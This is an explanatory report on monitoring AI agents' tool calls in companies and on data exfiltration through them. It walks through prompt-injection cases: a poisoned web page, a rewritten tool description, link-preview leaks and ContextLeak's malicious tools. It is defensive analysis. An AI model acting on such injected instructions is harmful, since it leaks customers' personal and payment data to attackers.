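# Monitoring what AI agents output and do in companies, and detecting data exfiltration through their tool calls

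## What happens when an AI agent calls a tool, and what does existing security monitoring see?

An AI agent is a language model that software runs in a loop so that the model can call tools and act on the results. Companies use agents to answer customers, check invoices and write code. These tasks require access to company data and usually a way to send messages or change records. An agent with both can also send data to someone who isn't entitled to it. This is called exfiltration, whether an outsider planned it or it happened by mistake.

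Software for monitoring corporate systems is decades older than agents, and was designed for people who log in and programs whose developers fixed the order of operations beforehand. Kim, Liu and colleagues (2026) point out in *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI*, a survey of 128 papers, that an agent can instead decide its workflow as it works, based on the task and the input it receives. An engineer can read a payroll program's source code and list the systems it contacts, but can't do this for an agent with a browser and a mailbox, because the model chooses which systems to contact while it runs.

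A monitor could in principle examine the agent's output layer, meaning everything the system emits: its final response to the user, its tool calls, its messages to other agents and its writes to memory. The final response is the part that people read, but an email the agent sent halfway through the task may not appear in it.

### One complaint, step by step

A retailer might have a support agent that handles complaints with three tools: one looks up a customer's record, one opens a web page and one sends email. A customer, Ana Ruiz, writes that the shop charged her twice for one order and links to a page where she has posted her evidence.

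*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) divides a run like this into five stages. The run starts with a request, in which the ticket system sends the agent the complaint and asks it to resolve the matter. The runtime, the ordinary software around the model, then assembles the context, which is all the text the model is given at that step. Here the context holds the company's instructions, the complaint and a description of each tool. Next the model proposes a tool call, a structured request to run a named function with given arguments. The runtime executes the call. Whatever the function returns, called the tool result, goes into the context, and the model either proposes another call or writes its final response.

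For Ruiz's complaint the model calls a tool three times. It looks up her record, which contains her address, her orders and her card number. It opens the page. Then it produces something like this:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "ana.ruiz@example.com",
    "subject": "Your complaint about order 4471",
    "body": "We have found the second charge and passed it to our billing team."
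  }
}
```

At this point the model has only generated text in a format that the runtime can read. Before the runtime sends the message, software can inspect the call, log it, hold it for a person to review, or refuse it. Once the mail system accepts the message, the model receives a success notice as the tool result and closes the ticket with a final response such as "duplicate charge passed to billing, customer informed". All the steps from request to final response make up one session.

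By the time the model writes the email, its context contains a card number from the company's database and several paragraphs from a website the company doesn't control. Shim and colleagues say the risk comes from this mixture. An agent is useful because it can combine information from many places, but this also puts material from different owners into a single context, even though the sources deserve different levels of trust.

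### What the Model Context Protocol adds

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for connecting AI agents to services. Without a shared format, developers would have to build a separate connection for each pairing of agent and service. Anthropic introduced MCP in 2024 (Granados, 2026, *MCP 2026 changes the rules*), and by July 2026 its main development kits were downloaded nearly half a billion times a month.

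Under MCP, a program called a server offers tools, and a client inside the agent's software connects to it. The specification page, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), describes the exchange. The server publishes a list of tools, each with a name, a plain-language description and an input schema that specifies the arguments and their types. The model picks a tool from the list, and the client sends the call to the server in a message with the method name `tools/call`. The client then passes the result back to the model.

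The same page gives security advice directly relevant to exfiltration: clients should show tool inputs to the user before making the call, and should log tool use for audit. These are only recommendations, so a client that keeps no log can still comply. The firm requirements apply to servers, which must validate inputs, control access, limit the rate of calls and sanitise outputs. It is also unclear which user would confirm calls made by a support agent that runs unattended. Ruiz would be a poor choice to approve lookups in the retailer's database, and an employee who approved every one would be doing much of the agent's job.

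The July 2026 revision of MCP also changed what network equipment can learn about a call. Previously, according to Cloudflare's *The next generation of MCP*, a gateway had to parse the body of a message to find out whether it invoked a tool. The revision requires calls sent over HTTP to carry two headers, short labels outside the body, that give the method and the tool's name. According to Model Context Protocol (2026), gateways can use these headers to route and authorise calls. The arguments stay in the body unless the tool's developer marks one for copying into a header, and the specification advises against marking personal data. So a gateway that reads only headers can record that the agent called `send_email`, but not who the recipient was.

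But another change in that revision makes monitoring harder. Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) lists the removal of protocol-level sessions, along with the identifier that tied one request to the next. That identifier was of limited use because a single server issued it, so it would have linked the database lookup to the email only if the same server offered both tools. The revision also documents a convention for attaching trace identifiers to requests, which could restore the link wherever developers adopt it. Some MCP traffic never crosses a network, because a server can run as a local program on the same machine as the client. No gateway handles those calls.

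### Prompt injection and the confused deputy

Now suppose someone posing as Ruiz sends the complaint. The linked page contains the supposed evidence, along with a passage asking whoever handles the case to send the account details to an outside address for verification. The model treats this request as part of its task. Its third tool call has the same form as before, but the recipient is different and the body contains a card number.

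This is prompt injection, in which someone places text in material the model reads and the model follows it as if it were an instruction from its user. In the indirect kind, which matters here, the attacker doesn't need access to the agent and only has to write something it will later process. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C explains why the fix for SQL injection doesn't work for prompt injection. In SQL injection, an attacker types database commands into a form field and the database runs them. Developers can prevent this with parameterised queries, which guarantee that the database never interprets the field's contents as a command. Language models offer no equivalent guarantee, because they predict the next piece of text from all the text so far, including both instructions and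 data. David C thinks it very possible that nobody will ever fix the problem completely.

On this account, a better model is the "confused deputy", a program with legitimate authority that someone else induces to misuse it. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988), the classic statement of the problem, describes a mishap at a company that rented out computer time. The company's compiler had permission to write in its own directory, which held its usage statistics and also the billing file. A user asked the compiler to write its debugging output to a file and gave the name of the billing file. The operating system checked that the compiler had permission to write there and let it overwrite the bills. Hardy concluded that the compiler carried authority from two sources, the user and its own licence, and had no way to keep them apart.

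The support agent is in the compiler's position. Its authority to read records and send mail comes from the retailer, while the wording of a stranger's web page influences what it does with them. Hardy could propose a repair, which was to make the program name the specific permission it was using for each file. David C argues that language models are "inherently confusable" and that companies should plan for the residue. In practice that means asking what would happen if an attacker had direct use of the agent's tools. For the retailer, anyone who can get text in front of the agent might as well have a customer lookup and a company mailbox. (The MCP documents also use the phrase, but for something narrower. In Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* it refers to a flaw in how an intermediary server obtains a user's consent to reach another company's service.)

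*Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), which the Australian Signals Directorate wrote with five other national agencies, illustrates the consequence for monitoring with a hypothetical procurement agent that has broad access to finance systems, email and contracts. An attacker compromises a minor tool in the agent's workflow, alters contracts and approves payments. Because all of this happens under a trusted agent's identity, the audit logs look legitimate and the company is slow to notice. The permission check passes for the reason Hardy described, which is that the agent really does have permission.

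### What each part of the security stack records

Large companies typically run several layers of monitoring already, and most of them would pick up some trace of the email.

An API gateway sits in front of a company's application programming interfaces (APIs), the connections through which programs call one another. It checks the caller's credential, limits the rate of calls and records the time, the caller, the address, the size of the exchange and a status code. A web application firewall often runs beside it, comparing requests with the patterns of known attacks and recording any match. Both are built to stop unauthorized callers and requests with something technically wrong in them. Their design assumes that a caller with a valid credential is a program doing what its developers wrote, and neither is designed to flag a polite email in English.

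Data loss prevention (DLP) software searches the content of outgoing mail, uploads and copied files for sensitive material. It then blocks a match or reports it with the sender, the recipient and the rule that applied. Its designers had in mind a careless or dishonest employee using a channel that the scanner covers.

Endpoint detection runs on laptops and servers, where it records which programs start, which files they open and which machines they contact. It is good at spotting programs that shouldn't be there. But the company installed the agent's runtime on purpose, and if a vendor hosts the agent, there may be no company machine to monitor.

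A cloud access broker records which account used which online service, what the account uploaded or shared, and whether the company has approved the service. It treats each account as representing an employee. User-behaviour analytics uses such records to model what is normal for each account and flag departures, such as a large download at three in the morning. This works best when an account belongs to one person with one job. An AI support agent may work through the night and open hundreds of unrelated customer records, so almost any single lookup falls within its normal range.

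A security information and event management (SIEM) system collects the logs from all of these and raises alerts according to rules. It can connect events that the other systems recorded separately if those events share an identifier. The SIEM does not have the text of the email unless one of the other systems kept it.

With fairly typical settings, the honest email and the leak would leave records something like these:

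| Part of the stack | Email to Ruiz about her refund | Email to a stranger with her card number |
|---|---|---|
| API gateway | Support agent, valid credential, `send_email`, 200 OK | The same |
| Web application firewall | No known attack pattern | The same |
| DLP | No match | Card number found, if the scanner covers this route and the number keeps its usual form |
| Endpoint detection | Agent's runtime opens an encrypted connection to the mail tool | The same |
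| Cloud access broker | Approved account uses approved mail service | The same |
| User-behaviour analytics | Ordinary volume for this account | Ordinary volume, perhaps a new recipient domain |
| SIEM | Routine entries from the systems above | The same, plus a DLP alert if there was one |

The two earlier calls also look routine. The agent reads customer records all day, and complaints often link to websites that nobody at the company has visited.

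DLP has a fair chance in this example because card numbers have a standard range of lengths and a check digit, which make them easy to recognise. A home address or an account of someone's illness is harder to recognise. Even a correct match shows only what the message contains; whether the recipient may have it depends on the recipient and the task. The same rule would have fired if the agent had quoted the card number back to Ruiz herself, although she is entitled to know it.

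According to guidance from the Australian Signals Directorate, tools perform many of an agent's actions and may do so outside the system's monitoring boundary. If another company runs the mail tool, for example, the retailer's gateway can record the request and the success notice, but not what the tool did in between.

### A valid credential, a correct schema and a "200 OK"

The leaked email passes every standard technical check. Its credential is valid because the retailer issued it to the agent for sending email, and the agent used it for that. A credential identifies the account that is acting but not whose idea the action was, and sometimes even the account is unclear. Some Model Context Protocol (MCP) servers pass a client's access token straight through to another service, which the protocol forbids. MCP's security guidance warns that the second service's logs may then attribute the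 request to an identity other than the server that forwarded it. Some systems also check an agent's permissions only once, at start-up, so an attacker can exploit the old approval long after circumstances have changed.

The schema correctly accepts both emails because it describes only their form. Each email has the required recipient, subject and body, all as text strings. A stricter schema could also require a well-formed address, but the stranger's address would pass that check too.

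The standard web status code "200 OK" means that the server handled a request successfully, so a tool call that sends an email to the wrong person can still return it. The code can also appear when the tool failed. Under the Model Context Protocol specification, if a tool fails for a reason such as an invalid date, the server returns an ordinary result with an error flag inside the body. A gateway that keeps only status codes may therefore count the failure as a success.

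Microsoft's incident-response team reached much the same view in 2026 when it described an attack on an invoice-checking agent. The agent used the analyst's own permissions to call an approved tool on a server already on the company's allowlist (its list of permitted destinations). Each action was legitimate on its own, and under default settings there might be no alert. Microsoft sells remedies for this, so it has an interest in the diagnosis, but the remedies do show that existing security tools can monitor more than they usually do. Its DLP product can inspect the arguments of tool calls, and its cloud access broker can flag external addresses that an agent has only recently begun to contact. Its SIEM can match an agent's behaviour against logs from MCP servers, but only if someone has configured those servers to produce and forward them.

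## How many organisations monitor what their agents do, and why is it rarer than monitoring APIs?

Microsoft's tools can inspect what an agent does, but only if someone has turned on the right logs and connected them. It is uncertain how many companies have done this. The available figures come from surveys in which security staff describe their own employers, and almost all the sponsors sell software for securing agents or the APIs they call. The reported share of organisations that can see what their AI systems do ranges from 6% to 68%, depending on the question.

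### What security staff report

The most reassuring figure in that range comes from *The Shadow AI Agent Problem in Enterprise Environments* (2026), a survey report from the Cloud Security Alliance, a non-profit that publishes security guidance. Token Security, which sells identity controls for machines and agents, commissioned the survey. 68% of organisations reported high visibility into their agents and automated workflows, but 82% had discovered at least one agent or workflow in the past year that security or IT staff hadn't known about. At least half of the respondents must therefore have given both answers.

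Both answers can be true, because a company that searches hard for unknown agents will find more of them, and one that found an agent in the spring may have had it under control by the time of the survey. The Alliance's explanation is that many companies know enough about their agents to run them day to day, but not enough to be sure that their controls reach every one. Companies most often found unexpected agents in internal scripts, custom assistants and plug-ins on language-model platforms, online software with built-in automation, and workflows that developers had made for themselves.

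"Visibility" in these surveys may mean knowing which agents exist, knowing what they are allowed to do, or having a record of what they did. Only that record would show where Ana Ruiz's card number went.

Okta, an identity-software company, surveyed 306 security chiefs and other senior security executives for its *Global CISO Insights 2026* (2026), finishing in June 2026. Respectively, 47%, 46% and 45% agreed with the statements "I know where my agents are", "I know what my agents can connect to" and "I know what my agents can do". Fewer than 30% strongly agreed with each. Okta describes the 45% as the share able to authorise individual tool calls based on context and intent. That goes well beyond the statement, which an executive could agree with after reading the agent's permissions once. Confidence was also a poor guide to practice. German respondents were the most confident, but 58% of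 them placed their own organisation in the lower two of four maturity levels, although the German sample was only about 26 people.

The largest of the surveys about agents is Cybersecurity Insiders' *2026 AI Risk and Readiness Report* (2026), supported by Netskope, a network-security company. In early 2026, Cybersecurity Insiders asked 1,253 security and IT professionals whether their organisation could prevent a risky action by an AI system, such as an agent deleting a code repository, before it happened. Nine percent said it could, 24% said it could in some cases, 35% said they would see the action only in the logs afterwards, and 32% said they had no visibility into agent actions.

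Cybersecurity Insiders summarises this as 91% of organisations discovering what an agent did only after the fact. That figure includes both companies that can block some actions and companies that might never find out. Counted differently, 68% of respondents could see at least some of what agents do. Some of the others may have had little agent activity to monitor, because 10% of the sample prohibit agents and 34% confine them to experiments.

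The 6% comes from a stricter question in the same survey, about AI use in general. It is the share of respondents who reported "complete" visibility, which meant seeing all AI activity, "including prompts, uploads, API calls, and MCP communications". Another 45% could see the AI applications their company manages but had blind spots elsewhere. A further 35% could see only network traffic, so they knew which domains the company's machines had contacted but not the content. The remaining 14% had no meaningful visibility.

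In December 2025 Digital Commerce 360 reported that 38% of organisations monitor agent decisions end to end. The figure comes from Akto, a start-up that sells security for agents. The company's own report, Vineet's *The State of Agentic AI Security 2025*, gives it as the share of organisations that monitor AI traffic end to end, including prompts, tool calls and outputs. That is about as close as any of these surveys comes to measuring how many organisations monitor outputs. But Akto counted "100+" respondents, where Digital Commerce 360 wrote of hundreds, and a random sample of 100 would have a margin of error of nearly ten points either way. Only 21% of respondents kept an up-to-date inventory of agents, tools and connections, so at least 17% said they monitored AI traffic end to end without having such an inventory.

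Salt Security, which sells API security, asked a better question about how long it would take to establish every action that a particular agent took yesterday. In its *AI and API Security Trends 2026 (H2)* (2026), 15.7% of respondents said they could do it in minutes, while 64.5% would need hours or days of manual work. Only 12.5% could consistently trace the full path of every agent, from the instruction through tools and APIs to the outcome. Respondents can misjudge this too, but they are less likely to be vaguely confident about a specific task than about "visibility". Neither Salt's summary nor the Alliance's article on the Token Security survey gives a sample size.

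In the November survey by BlackFog, which sells software against data theft, 62% of security leaders could identify the users or departments sending data to AI tools, but only 48% could produce any record of the types of data sent (Coker, 2026, *Half of Security Leaders Report Sensitive Data Exposure Through AI Tools*). In the same survey, 56% said that agents acting on employees' behalf fall outside their existing controls. The logs Ruiz complained about had a similar gap, since they showed who sent the email but little of what was in it.

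Estimates of how many organisations have had incidents vary even more. In the Token Security survey, 65% of organisations reported an agent-related security incident in the past year. In a second survey, run by the same Alliance in the same month for Zenity, another seller of agent security, the figure was 47%. Gravitee (2026), whose software manages APIs and agents, reported 88%, but its question also covered suspected incidents and data privacy. However the question is worded, companies can report only the incidents they noticed, so one with no monitoring may truthfully report none.

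In the Zenity survey (Cloud Security Alliance, *Enterprise AI Security Starts with AI Agents*, 2026), 58% of organisations said they took five hours or longer to detect and respond to an agent incident, while the support agent's email to a stranger would arrive within seconds.

### Where "21% have runtime visibility" comes from

Writers on AI agents often report that only 21% of organisations have "runtime visibility", meaning that they can watch what their agents do as they run. OODA Loop's *Most enterprises can't stop stage-three AI agent threats, VentureBeat survey finds* reprints a version of this figure from the technology site VentureBeat, which credits a Gravitee survey of 919 executives and practitioners.

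An older figure, also 21%, measured something else. In Akto's *The 2025 State of Agentic AI Security Report* (2025), it is the share of organisations with a fully maintained, up-to-date inventory of agents and MCP connections. But Akto headlined its press release "Only 21% of Enterprises Have Visibility" and wrote in the text of full visibility into agent actions. Digital Commerce 360 then described the figure as the share with complete visibility across agents' behaviour, permissions, tool use or data access. In a second article a week later, Digital Commerce 360 (2025) correctly described it as the share with an inventory.

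The broader wording was already circulating by then. In March 2026 the AIUC-1 Consortium, a group that promotes a security standard for agents, published a briefing with the same percentage. Help Net Security's *AI went from assistant to autonomous actor and security never caught up* reports it as the share of executives with complete visibility into agents' permissions, tool use or data access. The wording is so close to the coverage of Akto that Akto is probably the source, although the article doesn't name one.

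Gravitee may have arrived at the 21% figure independently. Its other published survey used a different sample, which IT Brief UK gives as 500 senior technology staff in the US and 250 in the UK, and measured agents rather than organisations. It found that 47% of agents were neither actively monitored nor secured. But the only 21% figure that can be clearly traced to its source is the share of companies that keep a list of their agents, which is weak evidence about how many monitor what those agents do.

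### Do companies monitor APIs any better?

No published survey appears to compare API and agent monitoring in the same organisations using matching questions, so the common claim that companies log their APIs carefully and neglect their agents is an inference from separate studies.

The nearest comparison comes from an early 2026 survey of 327 security leaders, in which Salt Security (2026) found that 24% had a fully automated inventory of their APIs. *The Era of Agentic Security is Here* (Schwake, 2026) reports that, in the same survey, 48.9% of organisations were essentially blind to traffic between machines and couldn't monitor what their agents were doing. *Some thoughts on Salt Security’s State of AI and API security report* (Osterman Research, 2026) puts the two figures side by side, but they don't establish whether monitoring agents is rarer than monitoring APIs, because the first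 is about keeping a list of APIs and the second is about seeing traffic. Traffic between machines also consists largely of API calls, so a company that can't see it has an API monitoring problem as well.

Akamai's *API Security Impact Study* (2026) surveyed 1,840 security professionals in ten countries. 77% said they had a full inventory of their APIs, but only 23% had one and also knew which APIs return sensitive data. (Akamai elsewhere describes the 23% as a share of those with full inventories, which would make it about 18% of the whole sample.) Salt Security's *API Security Blind Spots Could Put AI Agent Deployments at Risk* (2025) reported that 80% of organisations in a study with 386 respondents lacked continuous, real-time API monitoring.

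| What the survey measured | APIs | AI agents and tools |
|---|---|---|
| A full, current inventory | 77% (Akamai) | 21% (Akto) |
| An inventory that is fully automated | 24% (Salt Security) | No figure |
| Monitoring that is continuous or end to end | About 20% (Salt Security) | 38% (Vineet) |
| Knowledge of the sensitive data involved | 23% know which APIs return it (Akamai) | 48% have some record of the data types sent (Coker) |

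Companies seem to be much better at listing their APIs than at listing their agents, but the published figures for monitoring are higher for agents than for APIs. These figures don't establish that agents get more attention, because the samples and definitions differ in every row and Salt's standard for API monitoring is demanding. A company without continuous, real-time monitoring may still have years of gateway logs. Even so, the surveys don't support the claim that API monitoring is a solved problem.

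One difference is probably that an API gateway logs each request as part of its normal operation, while a usable record of an agent's tool calls often depends on someone deciding to collect it.

There is better evidence that companies were already monitoring machine traffic less closely than user traffic when agents began adding to it. In the Cybersecurity Insiders survey, only 14% of respondents said they inspect API traffic as rigorously as user traffic. Asked which kind of AI activity was hardest to monitor, respondents mostly chose API integrations, MCP connections and traffic between machines, and just 6% chose employees chatting with an AI system.

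The sponsors' interests affect both columns of the table. Akto and Zenity benefit if companies worry about agents, and Salt and Akamai benefit if they worry about APIs. A sponsor can make a problem look worse without inventing results, by choosing a strict definition, putting the worst number in the headline and recruiting people who already care about the problem. The choice of respondents can also make the problem look smaller. Akamai found that 40% of top executives rated their organisation's API testing as advanced, against 28% of the staff who combine development, security and operations. Okta surveyed only senior people, so its 45% to 47% may be too high.

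When asked whether they have a complete record of what their agents do, most survey respondents say they don't. The share without one was 62% in Akto's sample and 87.5% in Salt's, but it depends too much on the question's wording for either figure to be worth quoting alone.

### Why the output layer is harder to watch

When Cybersecurity Insiders asked security staff for the biggest barrier, 34% named pressure from the business to adopt AI faster than security could follow. Lack of skills came next with 25%, then older tools that can't interpret threats specific to AI with 21%, and budgets with 14%. In a survey by Dynatrace, which sells monitoring software, 51% said that the technical difficulty of managing and monitoring agents at scale was holding back their use. Buying a product will fix some of these problems, but others come from the way agents work.

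An API's specification describes a proper request, so a monitor can compare each request with it. If a payroll interface expects one employee number and one month, a request for every employee at once stands out. Tool calls have schemas too, but a schema for sending email accepts any text in the body, so monitoring software has to interpret the text to detect a problem. When Cybersecurity Insiders asked security staff whether their controls would detect sensitive data after an employee had an AI system rewrite a document as a generic blog post, only 8% said yes, 27% said maybe if certain keywords remained, 46% said no and 19% weren't sure. The rewrite might change a secret project's name to "our upcoming strategic initiative", and a filter searching for the name would miss it. The survey answers are expectations rather than test results, but data loss prevention (DLP) rules that match patterns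 do have this weakness.

Agents' credentials make monitoring harder because they are valid and sometimes shared. According to Okta, 21% of organisations govern agents' access with shared credentials or service accounts that have broad permissions. If four agents use one account, the log shows a single caller, so nobody can work out what is normal for each agent or tell which one sent an email. Salt found that 95.8% of the attack attempts it analysed came from authenticated sources. It says these are increasingly rogue agents but gives no number for them, so the figure is better evidence of the limits of checking credentials than of how often agents are the attackers.

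Many companies also rent their agents from suppliers, which run them on their own servers. When such an agent reads a mailbox that a third company hosts, the tool call may never cross the customer's network. The customer's firewall might record only an employee's request and the final response, and the customer can see the steps in between only if the supplier exports them. In the Cybersecurity Insiders survey, 28% of respondents relied entirely on the vendor's security for AI traffic between machines, without verifying it independently. Using more suppliers also adds work. In the Zenity survey, 44% of organisations used two or three agent platforms and 43% used four or more, so a security team might have to connect several exports with different fields and different omissions.

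Keeping full content also takes much more storage than keeping a short record of each call. Suppose an agent takes 20 steps on a task and its context grows steadily to 200 kilobytes, which is easy to reach once it starts reading documents. The runtime sends the whole context to the model at every step, so logging every request would take about 2 megabytes per task, or roughly 20 gigabytes a day at 10,000 tasks a day. Storing each new piece of text only once would cut this to 2 gigabytes. A gateway that writes 300 bytes per call would need 60 megabytes for the same work.

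A large company can afford to store the logs, but deciding who may read them is harder. A complete log of the support agent's work would contain the addresses, orders and card numbers of Ruiz and every other customer who complained. The retailer would in effect have a second copy of its customer database, in a system built for searching. If a security team asks for such a log to catch leaks, legal or privacy staff may understandably resist, because a leak of the log itself would be serious.

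That argument may never take place if nobody is responsible for having it. At the retailer, the support department might have chosen the agent, a data team might control the customer records, and the security team would run the SIEM. Each could reasonably assume that one of the others had turned on the logs. A third of Okta's respondents named silos between AI and security teams as a barrier, and 20% leave agents to whichever team deployed them, case by case. In the Zenity survey, only 15% of organisations said that more than three-quarters of their agents had a defined owner. The most common answer was that between 26% and 50% did. A company may also acquire an agent without a purchase to review, for instance when an employee enables a new feature in software it already uses.

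Another reason is that the first AI systems most companies used were chatbots, so the first safety products checked what people typed and what the model answered. That covers most of what matters for a system that can only answer. According to Vineet, security discussions at the start of 2025 still centred on prompts, and many of the controls companies have today are of this kind. Cybersecurity Insiders found that where companies can block something in real time, it is most often a file upload (48%) or pasted text (37%), both of which are employee actions. General frameworks for managing AI risk have a similar gap. Help Net Security reports that the US standards institute's AI Risk Management Framework and the international standard ISO 42001 provide for risk committees and documentation but don't cover technical controls such as validating the parameters of a tool call. A company could follow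 both and still be unable to find out whom its agent had emailed.

### How Claude Cowork's activity became visible

Claude Cowork, an agent in Anthropic's Claude app, is a good example because Anthropic documents in detail what customers can and can't record. Employees connect folders and other tools to it and give it tasks. It runs on their computers or on Anthropic's servers.

Anthropic's Compliance API let large customers retrieve records of their employees' Claude chats, but it didn't initially cover Cowork sessions. Companies could instead export Cowork events through OpenTelemetry, a common format for records of software activity. Anthropic later added Cowork and its coding agent, Claude Code, to the Compliance API in beta, and wrote in *Compliance API coverage extends to Claude Cowork and Claude Code* that this "closes a gap".

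The export is still off until an administrator enters the address of a system to receive it, much as someone has to set up the logs from MCP servers in Microsoft's SIEM. That system then receives mostly metadata. Anthropic's *Monitor Claude Cowork activity with OpenTelemetry* lists an event for each tool call, with its success or failure, its duration and whether the user approved it or existing permissions let it through. By default, the record omits the text of prompts, Claude's responses and the arguments of tool calls. It also omits the names of the server and the tool when Cowork makes a call over MCP. If an employee of the retailer used Cowork to answer Ruiz, the default record would show that some tool had run successfully, but not the recipient or the body of the email.

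A company can change this and record sessions in full by installing a setting on each employee's computer, but the setting applies only to sessions that start in the desktop app, wherever they run. Sessions that start on the web or in the mobile app send only metadata whatever the company does, and so do scheduled tasks in the cloud.

Events from Cowork's cloud sessions come from Anthropic's servers, so the receiving system must be reachable from the public internet, at an address that meets several conditions. According to Anthropic, cloud sessions send nothing to an address that fails them. The administrator can still save the settings, and events from employees' own computers can still arrive, so a security team could see a steady stream of Cowork events without realising that those from cloud sessions were missing.

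The default is sparse because tool arguments may contain sensitive values. Anthropic warns customers about this and tells them to plan who can see the values and for how long. Some older versions of the desktop app sent content when nobody had configured the setting, but current versions send only metadata. This change protects employees and customers from a careless logging setup but gives investigators less to work with. The metadata is still sensitive, since it includes users' email addresses and the paths of the folders they connect.

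The Compliance API provides much of what the Cowork export leaves out. It returns a transcript of each session from Anthropic's servers, including prompts, responses, the content of web and MCP tool calls, and a verified user. It also covers Cowork on the web and on mobile, where the export provides only metadata. However, the API is available only on the Enterprise plan, so Team plan customers have just the export. The beta also excludes Claude Code on the web and sessions run through Amazon, Google or Microsoft cloud services.

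The export also streams events as they happen, whereas customers have to request transcripts from the Compliance API. An investigator at the retailer could use a transcript to find the stranger's address and the card number in the email. But to learn of the leak the same afternoon, the retailer would need software that kept fetching new transcripts and could recognise the problem in this one.

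## How can data leave inside a tool call that looks legitimate?

The support agent's email to a stranger passed every technical check because it leaked data through the values of ordinary fields. MITRE ATLAS (2026), a public catalogue of attacks on AI systems run by the US non-profit MITRE, lists this as technique AML.T0086, "Exfiltration via AI Agent Tool Invocation". The agent puts sensitive information into a tool's input parameters, and the tool sends it to an inbox, document or server the attacker controls, "as part of a seemingly legitimate action". MITRE added the technique in September 2025 and marks it "Realized", its label for techniques attackers have used in real incidents.

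The definition covers tools "capable of performing write operations", which is too narrow. An agent with read-only access to the web can also send data out, because requesting a page sends an address and the agent can put data in that address. The definition also assumes an attacker, although an agent can disclose data to the wrong party without one. MITRE's companion catalogue of defences, D3FEND, connects attacks to the files, network traffic and other digital artifacts they involve. Its page on this technique, *Exfiltration via AI Agent Tool Invocation*, repeats the definition but doesn't yet list any artifacts.

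### Which field carries the data

Ana Ruiz's details could leave the retailer by at least six routes:

| Field | How the data could leave | Where a record of it might exist |
|---|---|---|
| Web address | The agent opens a page whose address includes her card number | The call's argument; the web gateway, if the traffic crosses it |
| Image or link preview | The agent's reply includes such an address, and the app displaying the reply loads it | The final response; the app's network traffic |
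| Body of an email or document | The agent pastes her record into a message or a shared file | The call's argument; the mail system or the file's history |
| Code push | A coding agent investigating the double charge uploads her record to a public repository as test data | The repository's history |
| Search query | The agent searches the web for her name, address and complaint | The call's argument; the search provider's log |
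| Argument to a third-party tool | The agent sends her whole record to an outside service that needs only her postcode | The call's argument; the provider's log |

Even when traffic passes through a web gateway, encryption usually hides everything in the address after the domain name, unless the company decrypts the traffic to inspect it.

Link previews can leak data without a tool call. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* explains that apps such as Slack and Telegram fetch a linked page to show its title and a thumbnail, which sends the same kind of request as a click. If an injected instruction leads the agent to write a link with private data in the address, the data leaves as soon as the reply arrives. OpenClaw, a popular agent, was vulnerable to this in its default Telegram configuration, and turning off previews prevented it. A company that logged every tool call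 but not the final response would have no record of the address.

An agent can also leak data through a shared document without naming an outside recipient in the call. If an attacker can already open the file, the agent only has to write the data into it, and the log shows a file identifier and some text. An investigator would also need to know who had access to the file at the time. The same applies to customer databases. MITRE ATLAS also lists generated images and videos as possible carriers.

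Microsoft's invoice-checking agent leaked invoice data through an argument to a third-party tool. The tool checked suppliers' bank details, and its developer pushed an update that changed only the description the agent reads. The new description included instructions to collect the last thirty unpaid invoices and attach a summary to each request, supposedly to help detect fraud. The tool remained approved because the setup didn't require anyone to review the change. The tool's server returned a plausible answer to the analyst's question and passed the summary to the attacker.

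### Possible causes and the evidence each one leaves

An investigator who finds Ruiz's card number in an outgoing call still has to work out why the agent put it there.

When an agent follows injected instructions, those instructions are somewhere in its context. In Ruiz's case, a full record of the session would show that the stranger's email address first appeared in the tool result from the linked page. The log has to keep the text as the agent received it, because the attacker can change the page later. The support agent has one tool that gives it access to private data, one that exposes it to malicious text and one that can send data out. According to the programmer and blogger Willison (2025), this kind of theft becomes possible whenever a system combines all three.

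A malicious tool can leak data even if Ruiz's complaint is honest. MITRE ATLAS distinguishes tools with poisoned descriptions, poisoned code and poisoned responses. Its examples of poisoned code include an email tool that sends the requested message but silently adds a blind-copy recipient. If the retailer had installed such a tool, the agent's call would contain only Ruiz's address. The extra copy would show up only in the mail server's delivery records or the tool's own code. This has happened outside the laboratory. ATLAS cites a report by the security firm Koi on a backdoored MCP server for the Postmark email service. Installed copies of a malicious tool may keep leaking data after the publisher or directory removes it.

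When the model has been tampered with, by contrast, the odd request appears in the agent's own tool call, but nothing in the instructions, the complaint or the web page explains it.

An agent can also do more than it was asked, with no attacker involved. The support agent might conclude that Ruiz's bank could reverse the charge faster than the billing team, and email her record to an address listed on the bank's website. The evidence is the mismatch between the request and the action, along with any explanation the model wrote as it worked, since there is no injected text to find.

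Ordinary oversharing is probably the hardest leak to notice. Suppose the billing team uses a ticket system hosted by an outside supplier, and needs only the order number and the amount. The agent correctly opens a ticket but attaches Ruiz's entire record. The tool, the recipient and the action are all what the retailer intended. If the agent does this with every complaint, software that learns normal behaviour from past activity will treat it as normal. To find the problem, someone has to compare the data in the call with what the billing team needs.

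### Experiments with malicious tools and models

Three studies from 2026 tested malicious tools and models, each giving the attacker control of something different.

Jia, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *ContextLeak*, studied how much information a malicious tool can collect from the arguments an agent passes to it. A tool normally receives only these arguments, not the rest of the agent's context. The attacker controls the tool's name, description and code, and publishes it in a tool directory. A user has to install it, but the attacker doesn't need to know which model the agent runs on or what the user will ask. Jia and colleagues trained a small language model to write the names and descriptions, rewarding it when a test agent chose the tool and passed it a close copy of the context. The resulting descriptions present the extra information as something the tool needs to work properly, without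 any obvious command.

In the main test, on 200 simulated users who weren't in the training data, the agent chose the malicious tool 92% of the time when the target was the user's prompt and 89% when it was the conversation history. When the agent chose the tool, the copied text had an average similarity score of 0.99 for prompts and 0.85 for histories. An exact copy scores 1, and the score falls by the number of edits needed to turn one text into the other divided by the length of the longer text. With six other models, including GPT-5.1, the agent chose the tool 56% to 85% of the time, depending on the model and the target.

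The rate was much lower in a real product. Claude Code, running Claude Sonnet 4.6, chose the malicious tool in 22 of 100 trials. Each trial offered 20 tools, whereas the simulated users in training had three to five legitimate ones, so the wider choice may explain part of the drop. A 22% rate could still be enough for an attacker, because the agent may pick the tool on any new task.

Jia and colleagues also gave four detectors 200 malicious and 200 harmless tool descriptions. The detectors missed 97% to 100% of the malicious ones and flagged at most 2% of the harmless ones. These results provide little evidence about how well detectors can check code, because the test tools contained harmless placeholder code. A working attack would need code that sends the data somewhere.

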